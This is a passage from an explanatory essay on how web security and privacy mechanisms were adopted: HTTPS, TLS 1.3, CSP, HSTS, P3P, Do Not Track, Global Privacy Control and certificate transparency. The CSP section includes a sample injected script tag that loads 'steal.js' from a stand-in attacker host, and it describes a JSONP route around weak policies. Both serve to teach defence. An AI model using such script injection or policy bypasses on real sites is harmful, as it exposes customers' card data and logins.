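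Browser makers put pressure on sites whose owners could already afford a certificate. For years, browsers had shown a padlock on encrypted pages and nothing on the rest. DeBlasio explains in *HTTPS in the real world* that this failed because people don't notice when an indicator is missing, many don't know what it means, and they can't do much about it anyway. In 2017, Chrome began labelling unencrypted pages "Not secure" if they asked for passwords or card numbers, and in 2018 it extended the label to all unencrypted pages. Site owners then had to explain the warning to their customers.

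The US government required all federal websites to support HTTPS by the end of 2016. The order directly affected agencies, which could no longer delay, but it covered too few sites to explain much of the worldwide rise in HTTPS use. Bucknall and colleagues count it, along with free certificates and browser warnings, among the changes that finally made HTTPS widespread.

Nobody has cleanly separated the three effects, because they overlapped. In *A Note from our Executive Director* (2025), Aas, the head of ISRG, puts the encrypted share at 39% when Let's Encrypt began and doesn't claim all the credit for what followed. Of the 100 largest sites, 71 used HTTPS by default in 2017, up from 37 a year before. The price of a certificate can hardly have held these sites back, so browser pressure and easier migration probably mattered more for them. Free, automatic certificates were likely more important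 for small sites, especially when a hosting company turned them on for everyone.

Google planned for Chrome 154, in October 2026, to ask permission before a user's first visit to any public site without HTTPS. Thompson and colleagues argue that an attacker needs only one unencrypted page load, so even a few per cent of loads is too many. In a trial, the median user saw less than one such warning a week. Browser makers tightened the rules in stages partly because a warning on every unencrypted page would have been intolerable in 2015.

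### TLS 1.3 and the equipment in the middle

The IETF published TLS 1.3 in August 2018, after more than four years of work. Part of the delay was caused by middleboxes, the firewalls, filters and similar equipment between a browser and a server. Some of them read the unencrypted start of each handshake and dropped the connection if it didn't follow the older format. In early 2017, Google turned on TLS 1.3 in Chrome but soon had to turn it off because a Blue Coat web filter was cutting users off, including pupils with school Chromebooks in Montgomery County, Maryland.

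The filter was at fault, but users blamed the browser. This gave every browser maker a reason to let someone else go first, much as companies had hesitated over IPv6.

To leave room for change, the 1999 specification included an instruction to ignore any type of record an implementer didn't recognise. For years, few new features were introduced that would have shown whether implementers had followed it. The working group eventually disguised the new protocol, TLS 1.3, so that its handshake looks like TLS 1.2 resuming an earlier session. The handshake carries the true version number in an extension that older equipment should skip, and browsers can add a dummy message solely for compatibility with middleboxes. Google engineers also devised GREASE, a technique in which browsers insert meaningless values into the handshake at random. A product that can't handle unfamiliar values then fails when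 its maker first tests it, instead of years later when such a value is given a meaning.

### Who may read the traffic

Other operators objected to TLS 1.3's removal of the older RSA key exchange. With that method, a bank could copy all the traffic in its data centre, give its monitoring equipment the server's private key, and decrypt everything without slowing the connection. TLS 1.3's normal handshake uses temporary Diffie-Hellman keys instead, so the server's long-term key no longer decrypts recorded traffic.

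The disagreement predated the protocol. In 1996, Hallam-Baker complained that firewalls could not read SSL traffic at all and that SSL had no way to hold keys in escrow. He argued that a company's information chief would not let secrets leave "via some encrypted stream I can't read", and that banks and nuclear power stations had a legitimate need to monitor their own networks.

Twenty years later, in September 2016, Andrew Kennedy of BITS, the technology policy division of a trade association for large American financial firms, asked the TLS working group to keep RSA key exchange. Banks decrypted copies of their traffic to detect fraud and malware, trace faults and meet supervisory requirements. They owned the servers and the networks. Decrypting at many separate points would be slow and expensive. Kenny Paterson, a cryptographer, said no and added that the banks had made their request when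 the work was almost finished.

Engineers sympathetic to the operators tried again. A 2017 draft described how a server could reuse one Diffie-Hellman key and share it with monitoring equipment. A later version required the browser to consent. Opponents replied that a stolen monitoring key would expose all the recorded traffic it protected, and that a feature meant for data centres would spread beyond them, because governments could require internet companies to use it on the public. They also thought operators had adequate alternatives, such as recording session keys on their own servers or keeping TLS 1.2 inside the data centre. At a meeting in London in March 2018, the working group found no consensus to continue, and the proposal went no further.

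Supporters of inspection took the idea to ETSI, a European standards body, which published a variant called Enterprise TLS later that year. The server keeps a fixed Diffie-Hellman key, and the operator gives copies to its monitoring equipment. Ordinary TLS 1.3 browsers can connect unchanged. The design includes a notice in the server's certificate that monitoring is possible, but these browsers don't look for it. The IETF objected to the use of its protocol's name, and ETSI renamed the variant Enterprise Transport Security.

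The operators' argument is strongest where one organisation owns both ends of a connection, since it is reading its own messages. It is much weaker when the other end is a customer at home who hasn't agreed to the monitoring and can't see it. The IETF couldn't prevent a server's owner from sharing keys, because either party to an encrypted conversation can always reveal its contents. It could only refuse to endorse key sharing or make it easy. A common oversight interface would raise the same question about agents, because a deployer has a good claim to read its own agent's records, but those records may include the words of customers and other firms who never agreed to that.

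### A default that changed quickly

The move to post-quantum key exchange was much faster. A large enough quantum computer could break today's Diffie-Hellman exchange, and an attacker can record traffic now to decrypt once such a computer exists. The replacement combines the existing exchange with ML-KEM, a new algorithm designed to resist quantum computers, so an attacker has to break both.

Cloudflare, which carries traffic for a large share of the world's websites, has supported post-quantum key exchange on its servers since 2022. In March 2024, it reported that nearly 2% of its TLS 1.3 connections used it. Google turned on an early version by default in desktop Chrome the next month. By late October 2025, shortly after Apple added it to iPhones, most human traffic to Cloudflare used it. The two measures differ slightly, and neither covers the whole internet, but the growth is far too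 large for these limitations to explain.

Few people had to do anything to get the new key exchange. Browser makers updated their software, Cloudflare updated its servers, and the websites behind those servers got it automatically. If a browser and a server don't both support it, they use the old one, so early adopters could still connect to systems that hadn't updated. Some connections failed anyway, because the new keys make the browser's first message too big for a single network packet, and some servers and middleboxes weren't built to handle a first message split across packets.

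Post-quantum certificates are harder to deploy than post-quantum key exchange. Key exchange needs only the browser and the server to change, while certificates also need certificate authorities to issue a new kind of signature. The new signatures are also much larger, and a handshake usually carries several.

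## Rules that websites declare and browsers enforce

TLS protects a web page on its way to the browser, but it doesn't check whether the page's scripts are malicious. A website can limit what happens after the page arrives by sending a machine-readable rule with it. The visitor's browser, which usually comes from a company with no connection to the site, applies the rule. A small shop can restrict its own pages in Chrome, Firefox and Safari without a contract with Google, Mozilla or Apple.

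Websites send these rules in headers, short lines of text that browsers and servers exchange along with each page. Companies have also used headers to describe their privacy practices and to pass on users' requests not to be tracked, with much worse results.

### A policy, line by line

Suppose the shop lets customers post reviews but fails to strip code out of them. An attacker posts a review containing a script, and every visitor's browser runs it with the same access as the shop's own code, so it can read card numbers as customers type them. This attack is called cross-site scripting. Content Security Policy (CSP) is a second line of defence for sites that have made this kind of mistake. The shop might send this policy:

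```
Content-Security-Policy:
  default-src 'self';
  script-src 'nonce-r4Nd0m7';
  object-src 'none';
  frame-ancestors 'none';
  report-uri /csp-reports
```

- `default-src 'self'` allows images, fonts and other resources only from the shop's own address, unless another line sets a different rule for them.
- `script-src 'nonce-r4Nd0m7'` allows only scripts that carry a matching nonce, a random value that the server generates afresh for each page load. (Real ones are longer.)
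- `object-src 'none'` bans plug-ins such as the old Flash player, which could run code of their own.
- `frame-ancestors 'none'` stops other sites from displaying the page inside theirs, where an attacker could trick people into clicking hidden buttons.
- `report-uri /csp-reports` gives the address to which the browser should report violations.

Now suppose the page contains two scripts:

```
<script nonce="r4Nd0m7" src="/cart.js"></script>
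<script src="https://attacker.example/steal.js"></script>
```

The browser runs the shopping cart script because its nonce matches, and blocks the attacker's script because it has none. The attacker couldn't have included the right value, since the server generated it after the attacker posted the review.

HTTP Strict Transport Security (HSTS) is a simpler rule. It makes browsers use only encrypted connections to a site:

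```
Strict-Transport-Security: max-age=31536000; includeSubDomains; preload
```

Without HSTS, a browser may first contact the shop over an unencrypted connection and wait for the shop to redirect it to HTTPS. Someone on the same café network can intercept that first request and keep the customer on an unencrypted copy of the site. Once a browser has received the HSTS header, it changes any unencrypted address for the shop to HTTPS before sending anything. If an attacker presents an invalid certificate, the browser blocks the page and doesn't offer the usual option to continue anyway.

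The `max-age` value, given in seconds, makes the rule last for a year from the latest visit. `includeSubDomains` extends it to addresses such as pay.shop.example. The rule can't protect a customer's first visit, because the browser hasn't seen the header yet. `preload` therefore signals that the owner wants the site on a list built into browsers. Google maintains this list for Chrome, and rival browser makers base their own lists on it.

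### Why rival browsers apply the same rules

Mozilla's engineers published the original CSP design in 2010, and both Firefox and Chromium, the open-source project behind Chrome, had experimental versions in 2011. Engineers at PayPal, Google and Carnegie Mellon University developed HSTS, which the IETF published as a standard in November 2012.

Once a browser supports either mechanism, it protects its users on every site that sends the header, so its maker doesn't need to wait for rivals to adopt it. Supporting the headers also carries little risk, because sites that don't send them work as before and browsers that don't recognise them ignore them. Companies that switched to IPv6 early didn't have this backward compatibility.

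Google had another reason, since it runs large websites as well as a browser. On a mailing list of the World Wide Web Consortium (W3C), which develops many web standards, Google security engineer Janc argued that the web needed better defences against its most common and most damaging kind of flaw.

A rule is more useful to website owners when more browsers support it, because writing a policy takes the same work however many visitors it protects. In the early years, owners had to write each policy more than once because Firefox and Chrome used different names for the CSP header and somewhat different syntax. A W3C working group combined the two versions into one specification, with editors from both Google and Mozilla.

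The W3C normally expects working independent implementations before it makes a specification a Recommendation, its final status. Browser makers also maintain a shared collection of tests, web-platform-tests. A typical CSP test consists of a small page, a policy and the result that a correct browser should produce. Anyone can run the same test in competing browsers and compare the results, which turns a vague complaint about compatibility into a specific bug that an engineer can fix.

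Browser makers still took time to reach agreement. In 2016, Chromium fully supported the second version of CSP, but Firefox and the browsers built on Apple's WebKit engine had only recently caught up. The shared tests also check only whether browsers apply policies correctly, so a browser can pass every test while enforcing a policy that provides no protection.

### Most early policies didn't work

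*CSP Is Dead, Long Live CSP!* (Weichselbaum, Spagnuolo and colleagues, 2016) examined the policies that websites had deployed. The researchers worked at Google and used one of its search indexes, which covered about 106 billion pages on a billion hostnames. About 1.7 million hostnames had a policy, but a million of these belonged to five e-commerce applications that repeated a few policies. Removing duplicates left 26,011 distinct policies.

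They then checked each policy for four weaknesses: allowing inline scripts (code written directly into the page) without requiring a nonce, leaving plug-ins unrestricted, accepting scripts from any host, and approving a particular host that an attacker could exploit. A policy with any of these weaknesses offered no real protection against cross-site scripting.

| Weakness | All policies (26,011) | Enforced policies aimed at scripts (22,425) | Strictest policies (2,437) |
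|---|---|---|---|
| Inline scripts allowed without a nonce | 84.4% | 87.6% | 0% |
| Plug-ins unrestricted | 12.0% | 9.4% | 14.3% |
| Any host accepted | 22.1% | 21.5% | 0% |
| Exploitable host approved | 75.8% | 79.2% | 41.6% |
| **At least one weakness** | **94.7%** | **94.7%** | **51.0%** |

The zeros in the last column reflect how the researchers chose the strictest policies. Even among these, about half failed.

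The most common weakness was the `unsafe-inline` keyword, which tells the browser to run inline scripts, meaning code written directly into the page. Many sites had their own inline scripts and would have had to rewrite large parts of their pages to do without the keyword. But code that an attacker puts in a review is also inline, so the keyword lets the browser run it too.

Exploitable hosts are harder to spot. Most policies at the time listed approved script hosts and used no nonce. Suppose the shop approves example.org, which has an address that returns data wrapped in whatever function name the visitor supplies. Programmers used this technique, called JSONP, to share data between sites. An attacker can inject a script tag that points to this address and supply malicious code in place of the function name. The browser runs the script because it comes from an approved host.

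The shop bears the risk but can't remove JSONP from example.org, and example.org's owner has no particular reason to remove it because it isn't a security flaw in the owner's own service. The median policy listed 12 hosts, and Weichselbaum and colleagues could bypass 94.8% of policies of that length. Of the 15 hosts that sites approved most often, 14 had exploitable addresses, although two of these were exploitable only if the policy also allowed another risky feature.

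A weak policy matters only once an attacker has found a way to inject code into a site. CSP exists mainly for that situation, but 99.34% of the hostnames with a policy would have got no protection from it. The true share may have been higher, since the automated checks looked for only some of the known bypasses.

The researchers recommended nonces instead of host lists and proposed the `strict-dynamic` keyword, which lets an approved script load others. Google had tried a host list on Google Maps Activities, an application with 4 million monthly users. It had to make five major changes to the policy in 2015, and the list grew to 15 entries, at least one of which was still exploitable. After switching to nonces and `strict-dynamic`, the team made no further changes before publishing the study. Google was promoting its own proposal, so this example is weaker evidence than the survey, whose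 checks other people could repeat.

### What the newest surveys find

Helme (2026), in *Top 1 Million Analysis June 2026*, counted CSP headers on 170,057 of 819,002 popular sites, or 21%. That is up from 79,549 sites in 2022 and 1,365 in 2015. *Security*, a chapter in the 2025 edition of HTTP Archive's Web Almanac, reports almost the same adoption rate, 21.9%, from a larger and broader sample.

HTTP Archive found `unsafe-inline` in 92% of policies and Helme found it in 46.8%, but most of the difference probably comes from which policies they counted. The 92% seems to cover only policies that restrict scripts, while the lower figure covers every policy, including the many that now do something else entirely, such as upgrading connections to HTTPS or preventing other sites from framing a page. Neither number is a failure rate, because modern browsers ignore `unsafe-inline` when the policy also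 has a nonce.

Nonces have become much more common, rising from under 1% of script rules in the 2016 study to about 20% in the Web Almanac. The comparison is rough because the earlier study counted distinct policies and the later one counted pages, but the increase is too large to come only from that difference.

HSTS is easier to set up, but many sites also configure it incompletely. Helme found the header on 252,846 sites, and only 21% of them had all three settings from the shop's example. Some sites may omit `includeSubDomains` deliberately, because some companies still have internal systems that don't support HTTPS. A site that has fully switched to HTTPS has less reason to set a short `max-age`.

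Platform defaults explain some of the growth. GoDaddy signs very few of its domains with DNSSEC, but 96% of sites made with its website builder send both HSTS and CSP. Because GoDaddy controls those pages, it can add a header to all of them without involving their owners. Site owners also keep headers long after browsers stop using them. Helme found 163,114 sites sending `X-XSS-Protection`, an instruction for a feature that browsers have removed.

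### Trying a rule before enforcing it

A strict policy can break a site. If the shop's payment company loads a script that the owner forgot to approve, customers can't check out. Report-only mode lets the owner find such problems before browsers enforce the policy.

The shop sends the same policy in a header named `Content-Security-Policy-Report-Only`. When a script violates it, the browser runs the script anyway and sends a report to the shop. The owner can then review the reports, add nonces to legitimate scripts and rewrite pages that can't comply. When the reports contain only attacks and oddities, such as code added by a visitor's browser extensions, the owner renames the header `Content-Security-Policy` and the browser begins blocking scripts that violate the policy. The owner can also enforce a loose policy while testing a stricter one.

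Report-only mode is useful only if someone reads the reports. Helme, who runs a company that collects them, found that 9,979 sites used report-only mode in 2026, but only 4.8% of all CSP policies included an address for reports. An enforced policy without an address can still block attacks, but the site's owner may learn about a broken page only when customers complain.

Trial periods can also last indefinitely. Email has a comparable mechanism called DMARC, with which a domain's owner publishes instructions for other companies' mail servers to reject, quarantine or simply report messages that falsely claim to come from the domain. Of the 398,597 sites with a DMARC record in Helme's survey, 51.4% were set only to monitor. Some of their owners may still be preparing to enforce the rule, but they are not required to do so.

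### P3P

The Platform for Privacy Preferences (P3P), which the W3C published in 2002, was supposed to let browsers act on a website's privacy policy. A site could describe its practices in a detailed file and summarise its use of cookies in a compact policy, a string of three- and four-letter codes. `TEL`, for example, means the site may use personal data for telemarketing.

Microsoft gave sites a strong reason to send compact policies. By default, Internet Explorer 6, 7 and 8 blocked cookies from third parties, such as advertising networks, if they came without a policy or with one that described unacceptable practices. But the browser checked only for unacceptable combinations of codes. It ignored codes it didn't recognise and didn't check for required ones, so a nonsense policy passed.

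For *Token Attempt* (2010), Leon, Cranor and colleagues collected compact policies from 33,139 websites and wrote software to detect invalid, missing or contradictory codes. They found errors on 11,176 sites, about a third. Internet Explorer's default settings accepted 98% of the faulty policies. Amazon's entire policy was the meaningless code `AMZN`, and Facebook's had been `HONK` in 2009.

Many mistakes were innocent, including swapped letters and codes from early drafts of the specification. But Leon and colleagues concluded that most errors came from administrators who wanted to keep browsers from blocking their cookies and didn't consider whether the policy was accurate. They found one faulty policy, `CAO PSA OUR`, 2,756 times and traced it to Microsoft's own support website, which recommended it as a workaround for a problem with cookies in frames.

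Better error checking would have caught these policies, but probably not those that were well formed but false. A technical blog had published one policy with the promise that it would get cookies past any privacy setting. The policy contained no detectable errors, and 4,360 sites used it. The researchers examined 30 of those sites by hand. They found no readable privacy policy on half of them, and none of the policies on the other 15 properly matched the codes.

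Internet Explorer did block cookies, but its decision depended on a site's description of what happened on the site's own servers, which the browser couldn't check. Regulators from several countries had agreed in 2002 that a P3P policy was legally binding. By 2010, though, the US Federal Trade Commission had not acted against anyone for a deceptive machine-readable policy, and posting a false one remained the easiest way for a site to keep its cookies from being blocked.

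### Do Not Track

Do Not Track was simpler still. When a user turned it on, the browser added the header `DNT: 1` to every request, asking websites not to track that person across sites. Microsoft and Apple added it to their browsers in 2011, and Google did in 2012. By June 2018 all the major browsers had it, according to W3C's *Do Not Track and the GDPR* (2018).

Advertising companies had more to lose. The Digital Advertising Alliance (DAA) said it had agreed at a White House event in February 2012 that its members would honour the Do Not Track signal as long as browsers didn't turn it on by default. In May, Microsoft, a DAA member, announced that Internet Explorer 10 would turn it on by default. eWeek's *Microsoft Sets Do Not Track as Default in Internet Explorer 10* reported that the alliance thought this could undermine the compromise. In October, the alliance's *DAA Statement on DNT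 Browser Settings* announced that the group would not require companies to honour signals set by a browser maker, and that its enforcement partners would not penalise companies for ignoring them.

The advertisers reasonably argued that if a browser sends the same signal for everyone, a website can't tell who cares about tracking and who never opened the settings menu. The W3C's working group agreed, and its specification required browsers to leave the setting off until a user made a deliberate choice. The advertisers also had a commercial interest in this rule, because few people change their settings, so honouring their requests costs little.

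Microsoft's supporters could answer that most people had never chosen to be tracked either. But a company could now justify ignoring every signal from Internet Explorer, including those from users who wanted to send one. Microsoft dropped the default in April 2015, explaining in a statement quoted in Windows Central's *Microsoft won't enable 'Do Not Track' as the default for 'Project Spartan'* that sites could otherwise argue that the signal didn't reflect users' preferences.

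Removing the default didn't oblige sites to obey the signal. W3C's *Tracking Preference Expression (DNT)* (2019), the final version of the specification, defines how a site can report whether it tracks people, but leaves the requirements for compliance to other documents. A site could report that it was tracking the user and still conform. It could also send no answer, and the browser could not verify the answers it received.

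The working group closed on 17 January 2019. Its final document says that deployment was too limited and that there was no sign of planned support from browsers, third parties or the wider industry. All the major browsers had been sending the header, so support was lacking mainly among its recipients. Apple removed the setting from Safari the next month. By then the setting could even harm privacy slightly. The University of Oxford's *Do Not Track* (2020) explains that trackers can combine such settings with other details to recognise a particular browser.

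### Enforceable rules and requests

The browser can detect and block the script or connection that a CSP or HSTS rule covers, so the shop's attacker doesn't have to cooperate. The browser's maker has no reason to ignore the rule, since blocking the attack protects its own users.

Do Not Track relied on companies that profited from tracking to stop voluntarily. A browser could send the request but couldn't check what a company did with the data it received. Better wording or more thorough tests of the header would not have changed this. The benefit would have gone to people outside those companies, and no gatekeeper could make the companies comply.

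A stop message for an AI agent could be an enforced command or just a request. If a firm's own ordering system refuses all further orders from the agent, the orders stop whether or not the agent cooperates. A message to a coding agent on someone else's servers is only a request, unless the provider has built its system to obey and the firm can confirm that it did.

Browser makers sometimes enforce a request by blocking the behaviour themselves. Safari and Firefox now block many tracking cookies whether or not the tracker agrees. This protects users from tracking methods the browser can recognise, but not from a shop that collects data directly and later sells it.

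### Global Privacy Control and California law

Global Privacy Control (GPC) is the successor to Do Not Track. A coalition that included Mozilla, DuckDuckGo, the *New York Times* and the Electronic Frontier Foundation announced it in October 2020. The browser sends the header `Sec-GPC: 1`, which is technically almost identical to the Do Not Track header. But GPC makes a narrower request, that a business not sell or share the user's personal data, and it refers to an existing legal right.

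The California Consumer Privacy Act, in effect since 1 January 2020, lets residents tell businesses to stop selling their data. Regulations that took effect on 14 August 2020 require covered businesses to treat a privacy signal from a user's browser as a valid request. In November 2020, voters approved an amendment that extended this right to the sharing of data for targeted advertising, starting on 1 January 2023.

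In August 2022, the cosmetics retailer Sephora agreed to pay $1.2 million to settle a case brought by California's attorney general, who alleged, among other things, that it had ignored Global Privacy Control signals. Advertisers that ignored the earlier Do Not Track signal had faced no comparable penalty. California enforces the newer signal, but only for its own residents. Colorado and several other states have since adopted similar requirements.

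The law doesn't give the browser access to a company's databases. Investigators can turn on the signal, visit a shop's website and observe whether the page still sends data to advertising companies. A later sale of data between two companies' servers is much harder to detect. GPC also doesn't stop a business from collecting data for its own use.

Whether browsers should send the GPC signal by default is still contentious. Brave and DuckDuckGo send it automatically, on the theory that people who choose a privacy browser have already expressed a preference. The Do Not Track specification accepted the same reasoning for products whose whole purpose was to prevent tracking. Chrome, Safari and Edge had no built-in GPC setting when California's governor signed another law, the Opt Me Out Act, on 8 October 2025. From 1 January 2027, the act requires browser makers to offer an easy-to-find setting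 that sends an opt-out signal. They don't have to turn it on by default, and they aren't liable if a business that receives the signal ignores it.

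## Public records that outsiders can check: certificate transparency

A browser can enforce a shop's security policy only if it has reached the real shop, which it checks using the site's certificate. This check used to have a serious weakness because any of the dozens of certificate authorities that browsers trusted could vouch for any site. Even if a shop bought its certificate from a careful authority, an attacker could impersonate the shop with a certificate from a careless one.

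In July 2011, an attacker broke into DigiNotar, a Dutch certificate authority, and issued fake certificates for many domains, including Google's. *Our Story*, a history by the Certificate Transparency project, which grew out of such attacks, reports that there were more than 500 fake certificates and that attackers used them to intercept traffic from Iran. The victims' browsers showed no warning because the signatures were genuine. Browser makers later removed DigiNotar from their lists of trusted authorities, but Google had had no way to learn about the fake certificate for its domains until someone came across it in use.

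Certificate transparency puts new certificates on public record so that a domain's owner can find any they didn't order. Google engineers designed it, and the IETF published the specification in June 2013.

### From submission to proof

The public record is a transparency log, to which entries can only be added. Outsiders can use cryptography to check that it is complete. When the shop orders a certificate, the authority first creates a precertificate, which contains the details of the certificate it intends to issue, and submits it to several logs. Each log returns a signed promise, called a signed certificate timestamp, to add the entry within a fixed time, often 24 hours. The authority copies these timestamps into the final certificate and gives it to the shop.

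When a customer visits, the browser checks the promises against its list of recognised logs and rejects the certificate if too few come from those logs. The browser doesn't contact the logs, since waiting for them would slow every connection.

At this point the browser knows only that the logs have promised to publish the certificate. Outsiders can check that they did so because each log arranges its entries in a hash tree. A hash is a short fingerprint of some data. Any change to the data produces a different hash, and nobody can feasibly find two inputs that share one. Here is a log with eight certificates:

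```
                 top
           /            \
       h1234            h5678
       /   \            /   \
     h12   h34        h56   h78
     / \   / \        / \   / \
    h1 h2 h3 h4      h5 h6 h7 h8
```

The bottom row contains the hash of each certificate. The log joins h1 and h2, hashes the result to get h12, and continues upward in the same way until one hash is left. It then signs and publishes this top hash.

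Suppose the shop's certificate is the third. To prove that the tree includes it, the log supplies the hashes h4, h12 and h5678. An auditor computes h3 from the certificate, combines it with h4 to get h34, combines that with h12 to get h1234, and combines that with h5678. If the result matches the signed top hash, the certificate is in the log, and the auditor has confirmed this without needing the other seven certificates.

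Doubling the size of the log adds only one hash to this inclusion proof. Since 2³⁰ is slightly more than a billion, the proof for a log with a billion entries needs about 30 hashes, which take up less than a kilobyte.

A consistency proof shows that the log has only added entries. Suppose the log had just the first four certificates yesterday, so the top hash it signed was h1234. Today it supplies h5678. The auditor combines this with yesterday's hash and should get today's. If the operator had deleted or altered the shop's certificate overnight, h1234 would be different and the proof would fail. (Trees of other sizes need a few more hashes.)

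Monitors are programs that download log entries and look for anything suspicious. Facebook, Cloudflare and others offer services that alert domain owners when a new certificate for their domain appears. An owner who doesn't recognise the certificate can ask the authority that issued it to revoke it. If the authority is at fault, browser makers can stop trusting its certificates.

The proofs can't show that an authority submitted every certificate it issued. The browser therefore rejects certificates that come without a log's promise to include them. A provider could keep its AI agents' activity records in the same kind of tree, and customers could then check that nobody had removed any. But an action the provider never recorded would stay hidden unless the system receiving the agent's requests refused any that lacked proof of logging.

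### Why authorities complied

Logging costs a certificate authority money and exposes its mistakes, while most of the benefit goes to site owners and their visitors. In the earlier five-provider example, no provider adopts such a mechanism without a gatekeeper. Google acted as the gatekeeper for logging through Chrome, and other browser makers followed.

| Start | Browser | Certificates covered | If the log promises are missing |
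|---|---|---|---|
| January 2015 | Chrome | Extended validation | Chrome hides the company's name |
| June 2016 | Chrome | New ones from Symantec | Chrome blocks the connection |
| July 2018 | Chrome | All issued after 30 April 2018 | Chrome blocks the connection |
| October 2018 | Apple's platforms | All issued after 15 October 2018 | Apple's software rejects the certificate |
| February 2025 | Firefox on desktop | All from public authorities | Firefox blocks the connection |

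Extended-validation certificates were a premium product. The authority made extra checks on the buyer, and Chrome displayed the company's legal name in the address bar. Google announced in September 2013 that it would hide the name if the certificate wasn't logged. Most authorities waited until the month before the January 2015 deadline to start putting log promises in these certificates, according to *Does Certificate Transparency Break the Web?* (Stark, Sleevi and colleagues, 2019). Some carried on without them, including Verizon's Cybertrust, which left them out of 8,550 of the 8,556 extended-validation certificates it issued over the next three and a half years.

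This was a mild penalty, since the site still worked. Chrome also exempted older certificates if they already appeared in a log.

### Symantec

The rule for extended validation soon exposed a problem at Symantec, one of the world's largest certificate authorities. In September 2015, Google found in the logs that a Symantec brand had issued an extended-validation precertificate for google.com without Google's permission.

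Symantec investigated and reported 23 test certificates that it had issued without the domain owners' knowledge, affecting five organisations, including Google and the browser maker Opera. Google's *Sustaining Digital Certificate Security* (2015) reports that Google's engineers then found several more questionable certificates within a few minutes, using only the logs, and passed the results to other browser and operating system makers to verify. Symantec then audited itself again and found another 164 certificates, for 76 domains.

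Google then required Symantec to log every certificate it issued from 1 June 2016. SSLMate, a company that monitors the logs, called this the second milestone towards mandatory logging. Symantec let customers withhold the full domain name from the logs. It intended this option for private internal domains, but several popular websites selected it by accident, and Chrome rejected their certificates.

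In January 2017, Google began investigating another series of failures. By March, the investigation had grown to cover 30,000 certificates issued over several years. SC Magazine reported that Google engineer Ryan Sleevi, who also worked on Stark's study, cited "a continually increasing scope of misissuance" and announced that Chrome would stop recognising the extended-validation status of Symantec's certificates. Google also proposed phasing out trust in certificates Symantec had already sold. Symantec objected strongly, as Tune The Web's *Thoughts on Google versus Symantec* noted at the time.

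The objection didn't save Symantec's certificate business, which it sold to DigiCert, a competing authority, later in 2017. All the major platforms eventually stopped trusting Symantec's old certificates. In 2011, investigators had learned about DigiNotar's certificates only after a break-in. By 2015, Symantec's competitors and customers could look for its mistakes themselves, so Symantec could no longer decide how much of the problem to disclose.

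### Root programmes and the CA/Browser Forum

Google's power over Symantec came from Chrome's root programme. A root programme decides which certificate authorities a browser or operating system trusts, and Apple, Microsoft and Mozilla run their own. If a major programme removes an authority, few websites will buy its certificates, because they cause warnings for a large share of visitors.

The programmes share a set of minimum rules, the Baseline Requirements, which authorities and browser makers write together in a consortium called the CA/Browser Forum. Google's *Chrome Root Program Policy, Version 1.8* (2026) describes these rules as consensus-driven and says no single organisation, including Google, can grant exceptions to them. But the Forum can't make a browser trust any authority, and each programme can add stricter rules. Google reserves the right to run its own programme at its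 "sole discretion".

In practice Google consults the certificate authorities first. Nineteen of them sent 98 comments on a draft of version 1.6, and Google's *Chrome Root Program CA/Browser Forum F2F 64* (2025) says the comments led to changes and a second round of review.

For years, Google required certificates to be logged to work in Chrome but did not require authorities to log every certificate they issued. An authority could sell an unlogged certificate to a customer who wanted privacy, and Chrome would reject it. This changed on 15 June 2026, when Chrome's policy began requiring authorities to log every precertificate before issuing the certificate. Two weeks earlier, DigiCert had stopped letting customers opt out of logging, citing the policy.

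### How much the requirement broke

Stark and colleagues examined whether websites would stop working as Chrome tightened its rules. They combined Chrome usage statistics, error reports from users who had opted in, the contents of 36 logs, and 75 discussions in Chrome's help forum. They also used records from Google's web crawler for three lists of sites, the longest with 1.9 million entries.

By early February 2018, months before the requirement became universal, 63.2% of Chrome's encrypted connections met the log policy. Few website owners had chosen to comply. Of the compliant sites among the 10,000 most popular, 42.4% used certificates that Cloudflare had obtained for them, and 26.8% used certificates from Symantec, which was already required to log the certificates it issued.

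The universal requirement covered 42.6% of connections in the week ending 2 September 2018, soon after it took effect, and 99.5% of those connections complied. Missing or inadequate promises caused 3.4% of the certificate errors that users saw when loading a page. The ten sites that caused the most errors of this kind had no promises, and eight were government sites.

People who did see the warning clicked through it 49.0% of the time, compared with 28.2% for all certificate warnings that Chrome allowed them to bypass. In the help forum, some users had switched browsers, including one who wrote, "I had to download another browser, which im starting to like." Others had turned off their antivirus software to try to fix the problem.

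Stark and colleagues attribute the low error rate to three things. A small number of authorities and hosting companies could do the work for millions of sites. Google could introduce the requirement in stages and fix problems while they were small. Browser makers could also respond proportionately when a log failed, for example by accepting its existing promises but no new ones.

The study's comparison with HTTP Public Key Pinning supports the point about who does the work. Pinning let site owners specify which keys browsers should accept for their sites, which also protected against a dishonest authority. But each owner had to set it up, and it was notoriously hard to set up correctly. Few tried, and Google decided to remove it from Chrome.

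Six of the eight researchers worked at Google and were measuring their own employer's project. They still acknowledged that it depended on large sponsors, and doubted that certificate transparency would have spread widely without Google and Cloudflare.

### What the logs can't do

A log can't stop an authority from issuing a bad certificate. On 17 October 2026, a researcher reported that eMudhra, an Indian authority, had generated eight of its signing keys with almost no randomness, so outsiders could easily work out the private keys. Anyone who did so could have signed a certificate for any site and submitted it to the logs, which accept certificates from any recognised authority. Browsers would then have accepted it until someone noticed. Google's *Protecting Chrome and Android Users from Compromised eMudhra Intermediate CA Certificates* (2026) explains that Chrome blocked the keys remotely,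 without a browser update.

The logs did help with the next step, ending trust in eMudhra's remaining root certificate. Google based the cut-off on the date of the earliest log promise, according to its *Upcoming change for eMudhra CA certificates included in the Chrome Root Store*. An authority can write a false date on a certificate, as the Chinese authority WoSign did, but it can't backdate another organisation's signed promise.

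Detection also depends on someone checking the logs. A bank probably pays for monitoring, but the owner of a small shop may never have heard of the logs.

A dishonest log operator could also sign a promise to include an attacker's certificate and then leave it out, or show the victim a tree that includes the certificate and everyone else a tree that doesn't. Chrome makes this harder by requiring promises from at least two operators, who would have to collude. The original plan also called for browsers and other clients to exchange the signed top hashes they received, which would expose two versions of the same log. Very little of this exchange was ever deployed, partly because a browser that asks a log about a certificate reveals which site its user is visiting.

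Google built a narrower check for Chrome, starting in March 2021. According to its design document, *Opt-in SCT Auditing*, Chrome sends Google a sample of the promises it receives, but only for users who have agreed to share security data. Google can then check whether the certificates are in the logs. These users have to trust Google with part of their browsing history, which is a compromise for a system meant to reduce the need for trust.

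Outsiders have caught failing logs without this exchange. In February 2017, a log run by the company Venafi published two inconsistent versions of its tree after an Amazon cloud outage, and an independent researcher's monitoring software detected the inconsistency. Chrome stopped accepting new promises from the log. Fewer than 2,000 certificates were affected.

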